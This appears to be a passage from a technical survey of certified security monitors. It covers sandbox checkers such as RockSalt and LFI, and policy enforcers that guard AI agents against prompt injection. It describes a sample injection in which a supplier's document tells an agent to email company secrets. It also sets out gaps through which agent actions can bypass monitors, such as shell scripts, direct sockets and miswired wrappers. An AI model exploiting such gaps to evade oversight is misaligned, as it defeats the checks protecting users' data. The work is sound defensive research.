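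No checker can verify that a policy is the one its author wanted. Jones and Hamlen, in *Enforcing IRM Security Policies*, describe two policies with such gaps. The first stopped the email client Columba from creating or opening `.exe` files. To write it, they had to list the Java library methods that can access the file system, including methods that create databases, since databases are stored in files. They admit that they compiled the list informally and that it probably lacks some methods. The policy also unexpectedly disabled Columba's spell-checker, a separate program that Columba has to launch.

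The second policy let users of XNap, a file-sharing program, download at most two more files than they uploaded. Users could get around it by restarting XNap, which reset the count, or by queuing uploads and then cancelling them. The printed policy also has two conflicting rules for a download when the count is 2. One raises the count to 3, and the other treats the download as a violation. In the version Hamlen and colleagues printed in 2011, the first rule applies only up to a count of 1, which removes the conflict.

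Cheko's parser matters as much as its analysis. The Java part reads the policy and the program, and identifies which instructions count as security-relevant events. The Prolog part then follows the control flow and solves the constraints. If the Java part misses a call to `Mail.send`, Cheko can accept an unsafe program even when the Prolog part works correctly. Cheko's soundness was proved on paper for a mathematical model, so the proof can't rule out a bug like this in the code.

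All four systems also depend on a virtual machine to protect the monitor. Before Java runs a program, a component called the bytecode verifier analyses it. Leroy, in *Java bytecode verification*, lists what this analysis must establish:

- Every instruction receives arguments of the right types.
- The program never takes a value from an empty stack or puts one on a full stack.
- Execution stays inside the method's code and always continues at the start of an instruction.
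- The program initialises registers and objects before using them.

The verifier uses abstract interpretation, as Cheko does, but with types in place of values. Without the verifier's guarantees, a program could disguise an integer as a reference to an object, or jump past a guard. Leroy warns that any bug that lets an ill-typed program through could allow an attack. Several researchers have proved versions of the algorithm correct, some of them with the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL, but the implementation in a user's Java installation may still have bugs.

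### Is the checker smaller than the rewriter?

Sridhar and Hamlen argue that a verifier is typically smaller than a rewriter, and changes less often, because it doesn't generate code. The published line counts don't support the claim about size:

| System | Checker | Rewriter or optimizer |
|---|---|---|
| ActionScript, one family of policies | 2,000 | 400 |
| ActionScript, three families | 2,000 | 1,200 |
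| Cheko and the SPoX rewriter | 14,300 | 7,200 |
| CertiBlock, for Scratch programs | 9,921 | 3,060 |

The ActionScript figures leave out the shared code for reading and writing bytecode. *A Service-oriented Approach to Mobile Code Security* (Jones and Hamlen, 2011) gives the figure for the SPoX rewriter, which excludes the library the rewriter used to read and write Java files. Cheko's figure likewise excludes the Prolog system and its solver. With these exclusions, Cheko is about twice as large as the rewriter whose output it checks.

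The claim does hold for the 900,000-line Java rewriter that Hamlen and colleagues mention, which is more than 60 times the size of Cheko. But that count includes a general-purpose tool, which may account for most of the difference.

Line counts are also a crude measure of risk. A bug in a checker threatens security only if it makes the checker accept bad programs, and is just a nuisance if it makes the checker reject good ones. In a rewriter, any bug that misplaces or weakens a guard threatens security.

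Certification therefore needs another justification, such as generality. A single certifier can check the output of many rewriters, as in the ActionScript system. This advantage is smaller for Cheko because the SPoX rewriter already accepts any SPoX policy, so certification replaces one general tool with another.

A better argument for trusting a certifier instead of a rewriter is that the certifier changes less often. The SPoX rewriter grew from about 4,000 lines in 2008 to 7,200 in 2011, so a proof about the first version would soon have been out of date. Fixing the flaw that Cheko exposed in vrenamer required a change to the rewriter but not to Cheko. Changes to the bytecode language require changes to both certifiers and rewriters.

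The best argument for a certifier is still that it provides what Sridhar and Hamlen call a second line of defence. Suppose a rewriter produces unsafe code for one program in a hundred, and a certifier wrongly accepts one unsafe program in a hundred. If these failures are independent, only one program in ten thousand will be unsafe and still be accepted.

The rewriter and the certifier may not be independent. If they use the same parser, as the ActionScript tools apparently do, an instruction that the parser misreads could escape both. If the code's producer is supposed to run the rewriter, a malicious producer can skip it and write a program by hand to exploit a bug in the certifier, which is then the only defence. If the recipient runs both tools, the attacker has to find a program that defeats both.

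Jones and Hamlen also tried the opposite arrangement, in which the recipient runs neither tool. A trusted online service rewrites each program on request and signs the result, and the recipient checks the signature. This suits devices too slow to analyse a program themselves. But the signature shows only who rewrote the program, so the recipient must still trust the rewriter, the service and its signing key.

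### Native Client: a small checker with exploitable bugs

Google's Native Client let the Chrome browser run compiled programs from websites directly on the processor. It used *software fault isolation*, a technique from 1993 that confines a program to its own region of memory. A modified compiler inserted the guards, and a separate validator checked the machine code before Chrome ran it. Certified inlined monitors divide the work in the same way, but Native Client's policy is fixed. As Morrisett, Tan and colleagues describe it in *RockSalt*, the program may access only its own data, run only its own code, make no system calls, and contact the browser only through fixed entry points.

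On 32-bit Intel-compatible (x86) processors, special registers held the limits of the program's code and data, and the processor blocked any access outside those limits. The validator had to make sure that the program never changed these registers.

The validator can't catch every forbidden instruction just by reading the program from start to finish, because x86 instructions vary in length, up to 15 bytes, and a program can jump into the middle of one. The processor then reads the remaining bytes as different instructions, which may include a forbidden one. Native Client therefore required an instruction to start at every 32nd byte. If a program calculated a jump's destination while running, it had to round the address to a multiple of 32 before jumping, an operation called *masking*.

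The validator had about 600 statements of C, a tiny amount compared with the compiler whose output it checked. Early versions still had exploitable bugs, as entrants showed in a contest Google ran in 2009. Morrisett and colleagues partly blame the validator's structure, which mixed instruction decoding with policy enforcement and made it hard to tell which instructions the validator accepted. In May 2017, Google announced that it was phasing out Native Client in most of Chrome in favour of WebAssembly, a bytecode format for web browsers.

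### RockSalt: proving the checker correct

In 2012, Morrisett and colleagues built a replacement for the validator and proved its core correct in Coq. In simplified form, the checker works like this:

```
while bytes remain:
    mark this position as a valid start
    if the bytes mask a register and jump to it: skip both
    else if they are a safe instruction with no jump: skip it
    else if they are a jump to a fixed address:
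        record the address and skip the instruction
    else: reject
accept if every recorded address and every 32nd byte
    is a valid start
```

The checker uses tables that Coq generates from short patterns to recognise the three kinds of code. It treats a mask and the jump that follows as a single unit and marks only its start as a valid jump target, so a program can't skip the mask by jumping straight to the instruction after it.

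Morrisett and colleagues call a machine state *locally safe* if the special registers still have their original values, the program's code is unchanged, and the next instruction begins at a position marked as valid. They proved that a program in a locally safe state always reaches another one after one or two steps. It needs two steps only for a mask and its jump. Since the program starts in a locally safe state, it can never leave its sandbox.

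The Coq version of RockSalt's checker has about 80 lines. The definitions of the checker and the x86 processor together take about 5,000 lines, and the proofs another 10,000. RockSalt checked a generated program of about 200,000 lines of C in 0.24 seconds, compared with 0.90 seconds for Google's validator. An earlier verified system for ARM processors needed about two and a half hours for a program of 300 instructions, because it constructed a new proof for each program. RockSalt doesn't need to do this because its proof covers every program that the checker accepts.

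An older checker for x86 shows why the proof has to include the checker. McCamant and Morrisett published a machine-checked proof that their sandbox rules worked for seven instructions, but they didn't prove that their checker enforced those rules. Kroll and Dean later found several bugs in the checker's instruction decoder.

### Lightweight Fault Isolation: checking every possible instruction

*Lightweight Fault Isolation* (Yedidia, 2024) presents LFI, a newer sandbox for ARM64 processors with rules so simple that its checker can consider each instruction separately. LFI gives each program a 4 GiB region, and it slowed the compatible programs in a standard benchmark suite by 7%. It appears in the documentation for release 22.1 of LLVM, a widely used collection of compiler tools.

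LFI reserves two of the processor's registers. One, x21, holds the address where the region starts, and the other, x18, holds the address that the program wants to use. The main rules are:

- No instruction may change x21.
- The only way to change x18 is to combine the upper half of x21 with the lower half of some other register.
- Instructions that read or write memory must use the address in x18, with a few exceptions.

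The upper half of an address determines which 4 GiB region it belongs to, so an address built this way always lies inside the sandbox. If the program tries to use an address outside the sandbox, the rewritten code accesses one inside instead. That may cause a bug in the program, but it can't harm the browser or other host.

One exception is the stack pointer, which the program can use directly. An instruction may read from the address in the stack pointer and then reduce the pointer by 8. If the pointer was at the start of the region, it now points just outside. LFI permits this because the memory on either side of the region is unmapped, so the next access through the pointer stops the program.

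Earlier versions of LFI had soundness bugs because the developers did not realise that some permitted instructions could change registers in unexpected ways. Sotoudeh and Yedidia (2025), in *Automated Formal Verification of a Software Fault Isolation System*, set out to rule out all such bugs. ARM64 instructions are always 32 bits long, so there are only 2³² possible ones, about 4.3 billion. The researchers went through them as follows:

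1. They ran LFI's checker on every possible instruction and kept those that it accepted.
2. They used a formal specification of the processor to work out what each accepted instruction does.
3. They wrote an invariant I, which gives the permitted ranges of the reserved registers, the stack pointer and a few others. It took about 20 lines.
4. For each instruction, an automatic solver had to prove that if I holds beforehand, no access outside the sandbox succeeds, and that afterwards either I holds again or the program has stopped.

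The process took about 20 hours on a 160-core machine for each of LFI's two memory layouts. It found no bugs in the checker but uncovered mistakes and omissions in LFI's written specification, such as missing details about the memory around the first and last sandboxes.

Morrisett and colleagues proved the Coq version of RockSalt's checker correct and then translated it into C by hand, so the C version could contain a new mistake. Sotoudeh and Yedidia avoided this risk by running the actual checker on every instruction, so their proof covers what that checker accepts. They still have to trust the code that loads a program and passes its instructions to the checker.

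The method works only because LFI never has to check two instructions together. The original design let the compiler omit some guards on the stack pointer if a later instruction made them unnecessary. Sotoudeh and Yedidia report that LFI could drop this optimization with little loss of speed. On 64-bit x86 processors, LFI has to recognise certain sequences of instructions as units, and there are too many to test one by one.

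A more ambitious compiler needs a more sophisticated checker. Tan (2012), in *Binary-Level Software Security*, describes a sandbox that moves guards out of loops, as in this program, which adds up a list of numbers:

```
p = mask(p)
repeat until p reaches the end of the list:
    total = total + memory[p]
    p = p + 4
```

The mask forces `p` into the program's region once, before the loop starts. The checker then tracks the range of `p`. If a read succeeds, `p` must have been inside the region, because the memory on either side is unmapped. Adding 4 moves `p` at most 4 bytes past the end, where the next read would stop the program. So the loop is safe without a mask on each pass, because the checker can use each successful read to bound `p` for the next one.

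### What the proofs take for granted

A proof about a machine-code checker depends on an accurate model of the processor. Morrisett and colleagues wrote a model based on Intel's manual and compared it with a real processor on over 10 million executed instructions, but they had copied one bit wrongly in a rare form of the `MOV` instruction. Tests with compiled programs didn't reveal the mistake because compilers seldom produce that form. They found it only when they tried to prove that no sequence of bytes could stand for two different instructions, and the proof failed.

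Sotoudeh and Yedidia used an existing model of ARM64 but had to remove some of its code for atomic instructions, which coordinate threads, because it crashed their tools. They considered this acceptable because they were not verifying anything about interference between threads. They also wrote the program that turns the model's output into questions for the solver. An error in that program, or in the solver, could let a proof of a false claim succeed.

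Compilation can introduce errors too. RockSalt's C version has fewer than 100 lines besides its tables, and Morrisett and colleagues judged the risk of a translation error reasonable. They tested it against Google's validator on over two thousand small programs, and the two always agreed. But a C compiler must still compile it to machine code, and Tan notes that one testing tool, Csmith, had found 325 compiler bugs. Even a compiler that works as designed can undermine security. If a program overwrites a password with zeros and never uses that memory again, an optimizing compiler may delete the overwrite as useless.

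Hardware behaviour is harder to specify. Suppose a write covers two bytes, one in unmapped memory and the other in the host's memory. The processor will stop the program, but ARM doesn't always guarantee that it will do so before changing the host's byte. Sotoudeh and Yedidia avoided relying on the order by proving that LFI is safe even if the processor always makes an instruction's other changes before stopping the program. The proof doesn't cover other hardware problems, such as Spectre attacks, which extract secrets from the traces left by instructions that a processor starts early and then abandons. LFI has defences against basic versions of these attacks, but the proof concerns only the official results of instructions.

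Finally, both proofs assume that the host sets up the sandbox correctly. LFI's run-time system, which nobody has verified, has to leave the surrounding memory unmapped, put the right addresses in the reserved registers, and handle the program's requests safely. The proofs about inlined monitors have similar gaps. The locking mistake in Mobile's package code was in a trusted library outside the formal model, and the Coq proof for Java monitors doesn't cover the phone's checker code.

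### Why an email limit is harder to check than a memory boundary

Memory isolation is a simpler property than most policies that inlined monitors enforce, because whether an address is inside the sandbox doesn't depend on what the program did earlier. A limit of ten emails does depend on the program's history. The tenth call to `Mail.send` complies and the eleventh doesn't, though the instruction is the same, so a list of permitted instructions can't enforce the limit.

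The proofs differ in how much code they must consider at once. In LFI, every instruction preserves the invariant, so the checker can check each one separately. In Native Client, it may take two instructions to return to a locally safe state. Cheko has to follow every path through a whole marked region before its invariant holds again. Testing every possible instruction, as Sotoudeh and Yedidia did, would be infeasible for such regions, because even pairs of 32-bit instructions would give 2⁶⁴ cases.

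The events are also harder to define. A processor's manual specifies which instructions read memory, write memory or jump, but no manual lists all the ways a Java program might send an email or open a file, as Jones and Hamlen found when they wrote the Columba policy.

A sandbox can still help enforce a policy about a program's past actions. A sandboxed program can reach the outside world only through fixed entry points, and Tan explains that trusted code behind them can add further checks, such as allowing a program to open files only in one directory. The same code could count emails. The count would be stored outside the sandbox, where the program couldn't tamper with it, and nobody would have to certify an inlined monitor. However, the counting code would have to be trusted, and like an operating-system monitor, it could enforce only policies about operations that cross its boundary.

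## What current agent policy enforcers leave trusted

An AI agent combines a language model, which only produces text, with an agent harness. The harness sends the model the conversation and a list of tools, such as `read_file` and `send_email`. If the reply contains a tool call, the harness runs the matching function, adds the result to the conversation and calls the model again.

Tool results can contain text from strangers, and a model may follow instructions it finds there, an attack known as *prompt injection*. Developers therefore put security checks outside the model, as in this sketch:

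```
tools = wrap(tools)                      # add a check to each tool
by_name = table of tools, by name
repeat:
    reply = model(conversation)
    if reply is not a tool call: stop
    result = by_name[reply.tool](reply.arguments)
    add result to conversation
```

The sketch follows sample code from *Progent* (2025), a system with rules about tool names and arguments. `wrap` replaces each tool with a version that first uses a *decision engine* to check whether the policy allows the call. Progent can also run as middleware in an agent framework, or as a proxy between the harness and the model. In *AgentSpec* (2025), each rule has a trigger, a condition and a response, such as asking the user to confirm a large payment. The system in *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) runs tools in a sandbox that can block access to files or the network even after the harness has allowed a call.

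Suppose a developer swaps the first two lines of the sketch. The table now holds the original tools, so no call reaches the decision engine. The policy may be perfect and the engine proved correct, but neither has any effect. Claims about an enforcer's security therefore need separating:

- **Policy consistency:** the rules don't conflict, and together they have the properties their author wanted.
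- **Engine correctness:** the decision engine gives the answer that the policy's definition requires.
- **Complete mediation:** the deployed wrapper calls the engine before every relevant action. It also has to give the engine accurate facts and obey the answer.

### Faults in the policy

Many agent policies start as company documents in ordinary English, which a language model turns into rules. In *NOMOS*, Yu, Kim and Choi (2026) measured how often such rules are defective. From the clause "authenticate the user before any action", the model produced a rule that blocked every tool, including the two lookup tools that perform authentication, until the user was authenticated. Another rule required the customer's confirmation before calls to eight tools that only read data.

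NOMOS compares each rule with the tool descriptions without needing a theorem prover. It repaired or rejected 37% of the candidate rules for an airline and 13% of those for a retailer because of structural defects. It also replays the rules over recorded conversations to find any that would have blocked legitimate work. One rule from the development stage would have refused 95.9% of the calls it covered in successful runs.

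Yu and colleagues tested the finished rules on the airline and retail tasks in τ²-bench, in which agents serve simulated customers. Among calls that changed data, the share that broke the clauses used for scoring fell from 66.3% to 2.6% in the airline tasks and from 30.8% to 6.9% in the retail tasks.

A well-formed rule can still be too weak. Yu and colleagues also compared NOMOS with Progent on the banking tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark for prompt injection. They used the version of Progent in which a language model writes a new policy for each request. Attacks succeeded in 46.5% of runs without a defence, 5.6% with Progent and none with NOMOS. Twelve of Progent's sixteen failures came from two requests to pay a bill, one of which said to pay it "like last month". Neither request named the recipient's account, so a policy derived from the request could not restrict which account was paid.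 NOMOS had a fixed rule that money could go only to accounts that the user had named or that appeared in the transaction history.

That rule also blocked a legitimate payment to an account that appeared only in the bill. Without attacks, agents completed 79.2% of tasks with no defence, 70.8% with NOMOS and 62.5% with Progent. With only 16 tasks, the difference between the two defences was not significant.

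Later changes to a policy can introduce faults too. Shivakumar, Priya and Gao (2026), in *Agenra*, give the example of an agent that may delete files A and B once each. The monitor goes through a list of permissions and uses up the first one that fits:

1. Delete B, once.
2. Delete A, once.

A developer then widens the first permission to cover either file. Deleting A now uses up that permission, so the agent can no longer delete A and then B, which was permitted, but it can delete A twice, which was forbidden.

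Agenra uses Lean to check whether a revised policy preserves every sequence of calls that the old one allowed. The researchers wrote 51 test revisions, and Agenra certified all 21 that preserved the old sequences and none of the 30 that did not. The check does not establish safety, since raising a limit from one email to two preserves every old sequence but also permits a second email.

*If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (2026) cites Amazon's 2025 announcement of a Lean-verified compiler that turns policies in Cedar, Amazon's authorization language, into logical formulas for analysis. *AutoCedar* (2026) passes errors found by Cedar analysis tools back to a language model, which revises the policy. The resulting policies were equivalent to the reference policy in 89.0% of 200 cases, compared with 66.0% when the same model wrote policies directly. The other 11% differed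 from what the reference's author intended.

Cedar is also stateless by design, as *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026) points out. It can't enforce a ten-email limit unless another program keeps the count and supplies it with each request. That program must also be trusted.

### Proofs about the decision engine

Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026), in *LEANGUARD*, built a decision engine in Lean and proved it correct. Their policies contain permits, requirements and prohibitions, which can refer to earlier events. A requirement might be that the agent has already looked up the order it wants to change. For a call in context c, the engine's answer satisfies:

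allow ⇔ (some permit holds in c) ∧ (every requirement holds in c) ∧ (no prohibition applies in c) ∧ (no rule produces an error in c)

The proof shows that the engine evaluates these conditions exactly as a separate definition in temporal logic requires. Missing data counts as an error and causes a refusal. LeanGuard also records an allowed call before the tool runs, so an agent cannot repeat a single-use action while the first attempt is in progress.

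The theorem takes c as given. An *adapter*, ordinary code written for each application, assembles c from the proposed call, the application's database and the history. If the adapter reports the wrong customer for an order, the engine will evaluate the policy correctly but use a false fact.

Sankar and colleagues tested LeanGuard on τ²-bench with five Qwen models. Without it, agents carried out at least 33 calls that the Lean policy forbids, and with it they carried out none. This count covers only violations of the Lean policy, so it can't show whether the policy captured all the company's rules.

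As a rough check, a language model judged the conversations against the original English policy. It flagged 9.7% of conversations without LeanGuard and 6.5% when LeanGuard was used and explained each refusal to the agent. LeanGuard had allowed every call that ran in the second group. An audit found that the judge was sometimes wrong, but also that the Lean policy omitted some requirements and that some records of customer confirmation were incorrect. Another model had produced those records by simulating a confirmation screen.

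LeanGuard also reduced the success rate of direct prompt injections on a second benchmark, DTap, from 57.9% to 5.9%. However, the share of harmless tasks that agents completed fell from 53.1% to 12.5%, because the researchers had not given them permission to change any data. In telecom, where the harmless tasks rarely required changes, completion stayed at about 75% while the attack success rate fell from 55.1% to 2.4%.

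Agenra's decision engine is also a compiled Lean program with proofs about the functions that run. Python code translates the policy, passes each call to Lean and then runs the tool. Shivakumar and colleagues list the remaining assumptions beside each of their claims and state that "none verifies the complete integration". One assumption is that Python runs exactly the operation and arguments that Lean checked, so every Lean proof would still hold if a bug in the Python code sent an email to a different address.

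Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues (2025), in *VeriGuard*, apply verification to guards that a language model writes. The user states a rule in English, for example that the agent may not email anyone outside the company. The model writes a Python function p to enforce the rule, along with formal conditions that p must meet. Nagini, an automatic verifier for Python, then tries to prove

{C_pre} p {C_post}

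which means that if the precondition C_pre holds when p starts, the postcondition C_post holds when it finishes. If the proof fails, the model revises its work and tries again. The model writes the conditions too, so the user has to confirm that they express the intended rule.

Nagini's proof doesn't cover the function's inputs. While the agent is running, a language model reads the agent's text and fills in the arguments for p. The instructions for VeriGuard's policy writer illustrate this step with a message to two people, one identified by an email address and the other only as "Dona Jhonson". The sample output includes the address `dona@example.com`, which isn't in the message. The verified function would then check a guessed address, while the email tool might use a different one.

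VeriGuard reduced average attack success on Agent Security Bench from 51.9% to zero with Gemini 2.5 Flash. A language model that judged each action directly, without verified code, also reduced it to zero, but agents using it completed 40.2% of their tasks instead of 63.3%. When the researchers added VeriGuard's components one at a time, attack success reached zero before they added formal verification, so this benchmark couldn't measure what the proofs contributed.

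In VeriGuard's evaluation, the success rate of attacks depended on how the harness used the guard's answer. When VeriGuard only told the agent about a violation and asked for a new plan, 11.9% of attacks succeeded, but almost none did when it also stopped the tool call.

### Weaving checks into an existing agent

FORGE, first circulated as PCAS, is the closest of these systems to a rewriter for inlined reference monitors. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) describes how FORGE instruments an existing agent with an *aspect weaver*. This tool adds code at chosen method calls, much as the SPoX rewriter does for Java.

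Suppose a user asks an agent to summarize a supplier's document, and the document contains an instruction to send the company's secrets to an outside address. FORGE handles this as follows:

1. Woven code records each message, tool call and result, and which earlier events could have influenced it.
2. When the agent tries to send the email, woven code pauses the call and passes its details to the decision engine.
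3. The engine finds that both the supplier's document and a secret file could have influenced the email.
4. The policy forbids external messages with that combination, so the woven code blocks the call and tells the agent why.

Either people write the policy in Datalog, a logic language whose queries always terminate, or a language model translates it from English. FORGE checks that the translation covers each requirement and that every rule is based on the original text. Soufflé, an existing Datalog system, evaluates the rules.

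Palumbo and colleagues tested FORGE with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, in five rounds of 97 harmless tasks and 949 attacks. When the user's request was repeated to the model after each batch of tool results, 14.1% of attacks succeeded. Adding FORGE reduced this to 0.9%, but completion of the harmless tasks fell from 83.7% to 62.5%. On τ²-bench's customer service tasks, average success across three leading models rose with FORGE, from 74.7% to 81.5% for the airline and from 86.3% to 87.4% for the retailer. Most of the gain came in tasks where FORGE had blocked at least one call. The engine typically took less than a millisecond to decide.

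FORGE's guarantee rests on complete mediation and on what Palumbo and colleagues call faithful observation, meaning that the recorded facts are accurate. Both depend on whether the weaver covers the right methods. It covers the functions that run tools in several agent frameworks, including LangChain, and the methods that send web requests in two Python libraries, `httpx` and `requests`. Palumbo and colleagues say in the appendix that covering these libraries prevents actions from bypassing the monitor by going around the framework, but they acknowledge in the limitations section that code can still write directly to a network socket. The RSSOwl policy had the same kind of gap, because it missed some ways to open a file in Java.

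Concurrency can also make the recorded facts incomplete. If a woven method starts several tasks at once, one of them may request an action before FORGE has recorded an event that influenced it. The engine would then decide without that event.

No separate checker examines the woven agent for missing coverage, and the main experiments don't include a search for actions that bypass the monitor. An inlined monitor is also harder to protect in Python than in Java. Cheko could rely on Java to keep other classes from changing the monitor's private variables, but Shivakumar and colleagues acknowledge that the boundary around Agenra's Python interface does not isolate arbitrary Python code in the same process.

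### Moving the check below the harness

Many agents have a tool that runs shell commands or scripts. A script can send an email without calling `send_email`, so a wrapper around the email tool won't detect it. *Kairos* (2026) argues that checking a declared set of tools makes complete mediation an assumption about the deployment. Kairos instead monitors the boundary of the agent's isolated environment, where effects look the same whether they come from a tool or a script.

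*Stop Means Stop* (2026) compares several ways to make sure that calls pass through its monitor. One scans the harness's code for direct tool calls made outside the wrapper, but it can't follow calls whose target the harness chooses at run time. The sketch at the start of this section chooses each tool from a table at run time, so the scan could miss the swapped lines. A stronger option is to configure the operating system's network so that tools can reach only the monitor. In a test of this setup, an attempt to connect directly to the outside failed.

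Counting the paths from an agent to the operating system is difficult even for a system's own developer. *Governed MCP* (2026) first reported that its system mediated all 123 paths. A later count with a rebuilt test found 59, of which the system mediated 43, and the developer withdrew the original claim.

Tether, which Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, developed for agents that use a command line, observes what each command does before letting it take effect. Their example has three steps:

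```
1  upload report.txt
2  copy servers.csv to report.txt
3  upload report.txt
```

The file `servers.csv` is secret. Steps 1 and 3 are the same command, but by step 3 the report contains the secret data. Tether runs each command on a temporary copy of the file system, records its requests to the operating system and holds back its network traffic. From these records it infers actions such as "copy" and "upload". After the copy in step 2, the report counts as sensitive, so the policy allows the upload in step 1 and forbids the one in step 3. If the policy allows a command, Tether makes its effects permanent; otherwise it discards them.

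The policy language is part of Lean, so a policy writer can prove that a policy meets a stated goal, such as preventing network access after the agent reads a sensitive file. Lean also runs the definitions used in these proofs as the monitor. Sistla and colleagues suggest that a faster version could run in another language, with automated tests comparing its answers with Lean's, as Cedar's developers do.

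The proofs do not cover the step that infers actions from operating-system requests, which the researchers tested on many generated inputs. When Tether cannot determine whether data has moved, it treats the data as moved. For example, if a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats the second as containing data from the first.

On two benchmarks for coding agents, Tether blocked every attack that the researchers counted as in scope, and wrongly blocked 2.3% and 5.0% of harmless runs. They excluded runs involving databases or background programs that Tether could not trace, and attacks that broke no rule about data or system access. The operating system, the sandbox and the network proxy remain trusted.

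### Checking programs that agents write

Some systems have the agent write a whole program, then check it before running any of it. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) requires the agent's program to type-check together with the developer's surrounding code. The types can express which files a program may use or where its data came from. This resembles Mobile's approach, except that the agent writes code to fit the types, whereas Mobile's rewriter adds annotations to existing bytecode. *L3M* (2026) similarly uses Lean to check extensions that agents write for themselves.

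CaMeL, a 2025 defence against prompt injection, also has a model write a program, but it checks the origin of the data while the program runs. Yu and colleagues report that it completed 77% of tasks in its main configuration, compared with 84% without the defence. Across six configurations, the loss ranged from 3 to 32 percentage points. CaMeL's programs use a restricted form of Python, and *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) warns that exceptions and reflection in this language make static analysis difficult. Both features also complicated the certification of Java monitors.

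*Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) applies the idea of proof-carrying code to single tool calls. The agent must supply a proof that its call keeps to an agreed contract, whatever result the tool returns, and a checker called the Airlock refuses any call without a valid proof. The guarantee assumes that the model of each tool includes everything the tool can do.

*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) comes closest to a certified harness. It presents a small programming language for agents and an interpreter, written in Lean, that runs the programs and calls the language model. It proves limits on how secret or untrusted data can influence the results of any agent written in the language. The paper describes this as the first formally verified agent harness. An existing Python agent would have to be rewritten in the new language to get these guarantees. *L3M* also points out that LLMbda models its tools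 inside the program.

### The missing certificate for instrumented harnesses

The systems that work with ordinary agents and tools establish different parts of the security claim:

| System | Source of the policy | Source of the enforcement code | Policy consistency | Engine correctness | Complete mediation |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| NOMOS | a model extracts rules from a document | fixed gate that applies the rules | static checks and replay | tested | assumed |
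| VeriGuard | a user's request in English | a model writes a Python function | the user reviews the conditions | Nagini proves that the function meets the conditions | assumed, and a model supplies the inputs |
| LeanGuard | a model drafts Lean rules and people correct them | Lean engine and an adapter for each application | human review | proved | assumed |
| Agenra | the application's developer | Lean engine and Python code | proofs about revisions, and searches up to a chosen length | proved for selected functions | assumed |
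| FORGE | people, or a model's translation | an aspect weaver | static analysis and translation checks | relies on Soufflé | assumed for the methods it instruments |
| Tether | people write Lean rules | sandbox and Lean monitor | proved for chosen goals | Lean runs the definitions used in the proofs | relies on the sandbox and tested inference |

Fifteen arXiv searches on December 6, 2026 found no tool that certifies an instrumented harness. Such a tool would prove that every relevant action in the harness passes through the checks that a weaver or developer has added. About seven of the searches were on certification, mediation or rewriting, and all were limited to arXiv, so a commercial or unpublished tool may exist.

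*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives machine-checked definitions of an agent and its monitor, but its rule for each request already includes the monitor's decision. Complete mediation is therefore built into the model, and a developer would still have to show that a real harness matches the model. *Agentproof* (2026) extracts a graph of an agent's possible steps and looks for paths that reach a sensitive tool without a required check, such as human approval. This is closer to what a certifier does, but the result applies to the real harness only if the graph includes every path in the harness's code.

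## Certifying the wrapper of an agent harness: a worked design

This section applies the published methods to an invented AI agent harness that nobody has implemented or tested. The harness gives the model three tools, `read_file`, `send_email` and `shell`. Its policy allows at most ten emails per session and forbids email once the agent has read a confidential file.

### Turning two rules into an automaton

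The policy's author first has to decide what the words in these rules mean:

- A *session* is one run of the harness process, starting with an empty conversation.
- An *email* is one call to `do_send`, the function that passes a message to the mail server. It takes one address and plain text. With a list of addresses, one call could reach a thousand people, and with attachments, the function would read files that the monitor never sees. Agenra, the Lean-based monitor by Shivakumar and colleagues, charges for each recipient separately, even if two of the addresses are the same.
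- A *confidential read* is a call to `do_read` on a path for which a function called `confidential` returns true. The policy's author supplies this function.
- Every call to `do_shell` counts as a confidential read too, because a command can open any file and the harness can't reliably determine which.

All these events happen when the call starts, whether or not it later succeeds.

The harness has to keep the count itself. The July 2026 revision of the Model Context Protocol (2026), a standard for connecting agents to outside tools, removed sessions, so a tool server that needs to remember earlier calls now issues an identifier, which the agent passes back as an ordinary argument. If a mail server counted emails by identifier, the limit would hold only if the model used the same identifier every time.

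The conversation has to start empty because an old one may contain confidential text. If the harness reloaded such a conversation but reset its monitor variables to 0, the model could email the text immediately. A harness that resumes old sessions must therefore save the monitor state along with the conversation.

The policy state is a pair (c, n), where c is 1 after a confidential read and n is the number of emails so far. It starts at (0, 0), and there are 22 possible states:

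- δ((c, n), read) = {(1, n)}
- δ((c, n), shell) = {(1, n)}
- δ((0, n), send) = {(0, n + 1)} for n from 0 to 9
- δ((0, 10), send) = ∅
- δ((1, n), send) = ∅

Reading a file that isn't confidential is not an event.

### The wrapper

Every tool call that the model requests goes through this function:

```
secret = 0
sent = 0

call(tool, args):
    hold the lock until this function ends:
        if tool == "read_file":
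            path = resolve(args.path)
            if confidential(path): secret = 1
            return do_read(path)
        if tool == "shell":
            secret = 1
            return do_shell(args.command)
        if tool == "send_email":
            if secret != 0 or sent >= 10: return "refused"
            sent = sent + 1
            return do_send(args.address, args.text)
        return "unknown tool"
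```

The function `resolve` turns a path such as `../plans/q3.txt` into a full file name, so `confidential` and `do_read` receive the same name. When the policy forbids an email, the wrapper returns a refusal and lets the agent continue. This doesn't affect policy adherence, because a refused call produces no event.

The wrapper holds the lock until the tool finishes because the rule against sending after reading is not race-free. As a result, a slow shell command delays every other tool call, and a tool that started a second agent and waited for its answer would deadlock the harness as soon as that agent requested a tool.

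### What the certifier must derive

Let C and N be the two parts of the policy state. The synchronization invariant is:

C = `secret` and N = `sent`, where `secret` is 0 or 1 and `sent` is between 0 and 10

It must be true whenever no thread holds the lock. It is true at the start, when all four values are 0. Because of the ranges, the certifier does not have to handle impossible cases, such as a count of −3, for which the automaton has no transition.

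Inside the wrapper, the monitor state briefly runs ahead of the policy state, because each update comes just before its event. At each tool call, the certifier has to derive these facts:

| Call | Known just before the call | Effect on the policy state | Known afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| `do_read`, confidential path | `secret` = 1, N = `sent` | C becomes 1 | the invariant |
| `do_read`, other path | the invariant | none | the invariant |
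| `do_shell` | `secret` = 1, N = `sent` | C becomes 1 | the invariant |
| `do_send` | C = `secret` = 0, N = `sent` − 1, N ≤ 9 | N goes up by 1 | the invariant |

The last row is the one that prevents violations. An email breaks the policy only if C is 1 or N is 10, and the guard has ruled out both.

For `do_read`, the certifier also has to check that the wrapper tests the same value it passes to the call. It can use a number K that is 1 if `path` is confidential and 0 if not, as Cheko does for text patterns. If the wrapper tested `args.path` but then read `path`, K would describe the wrong value and the certifier would reject the code.

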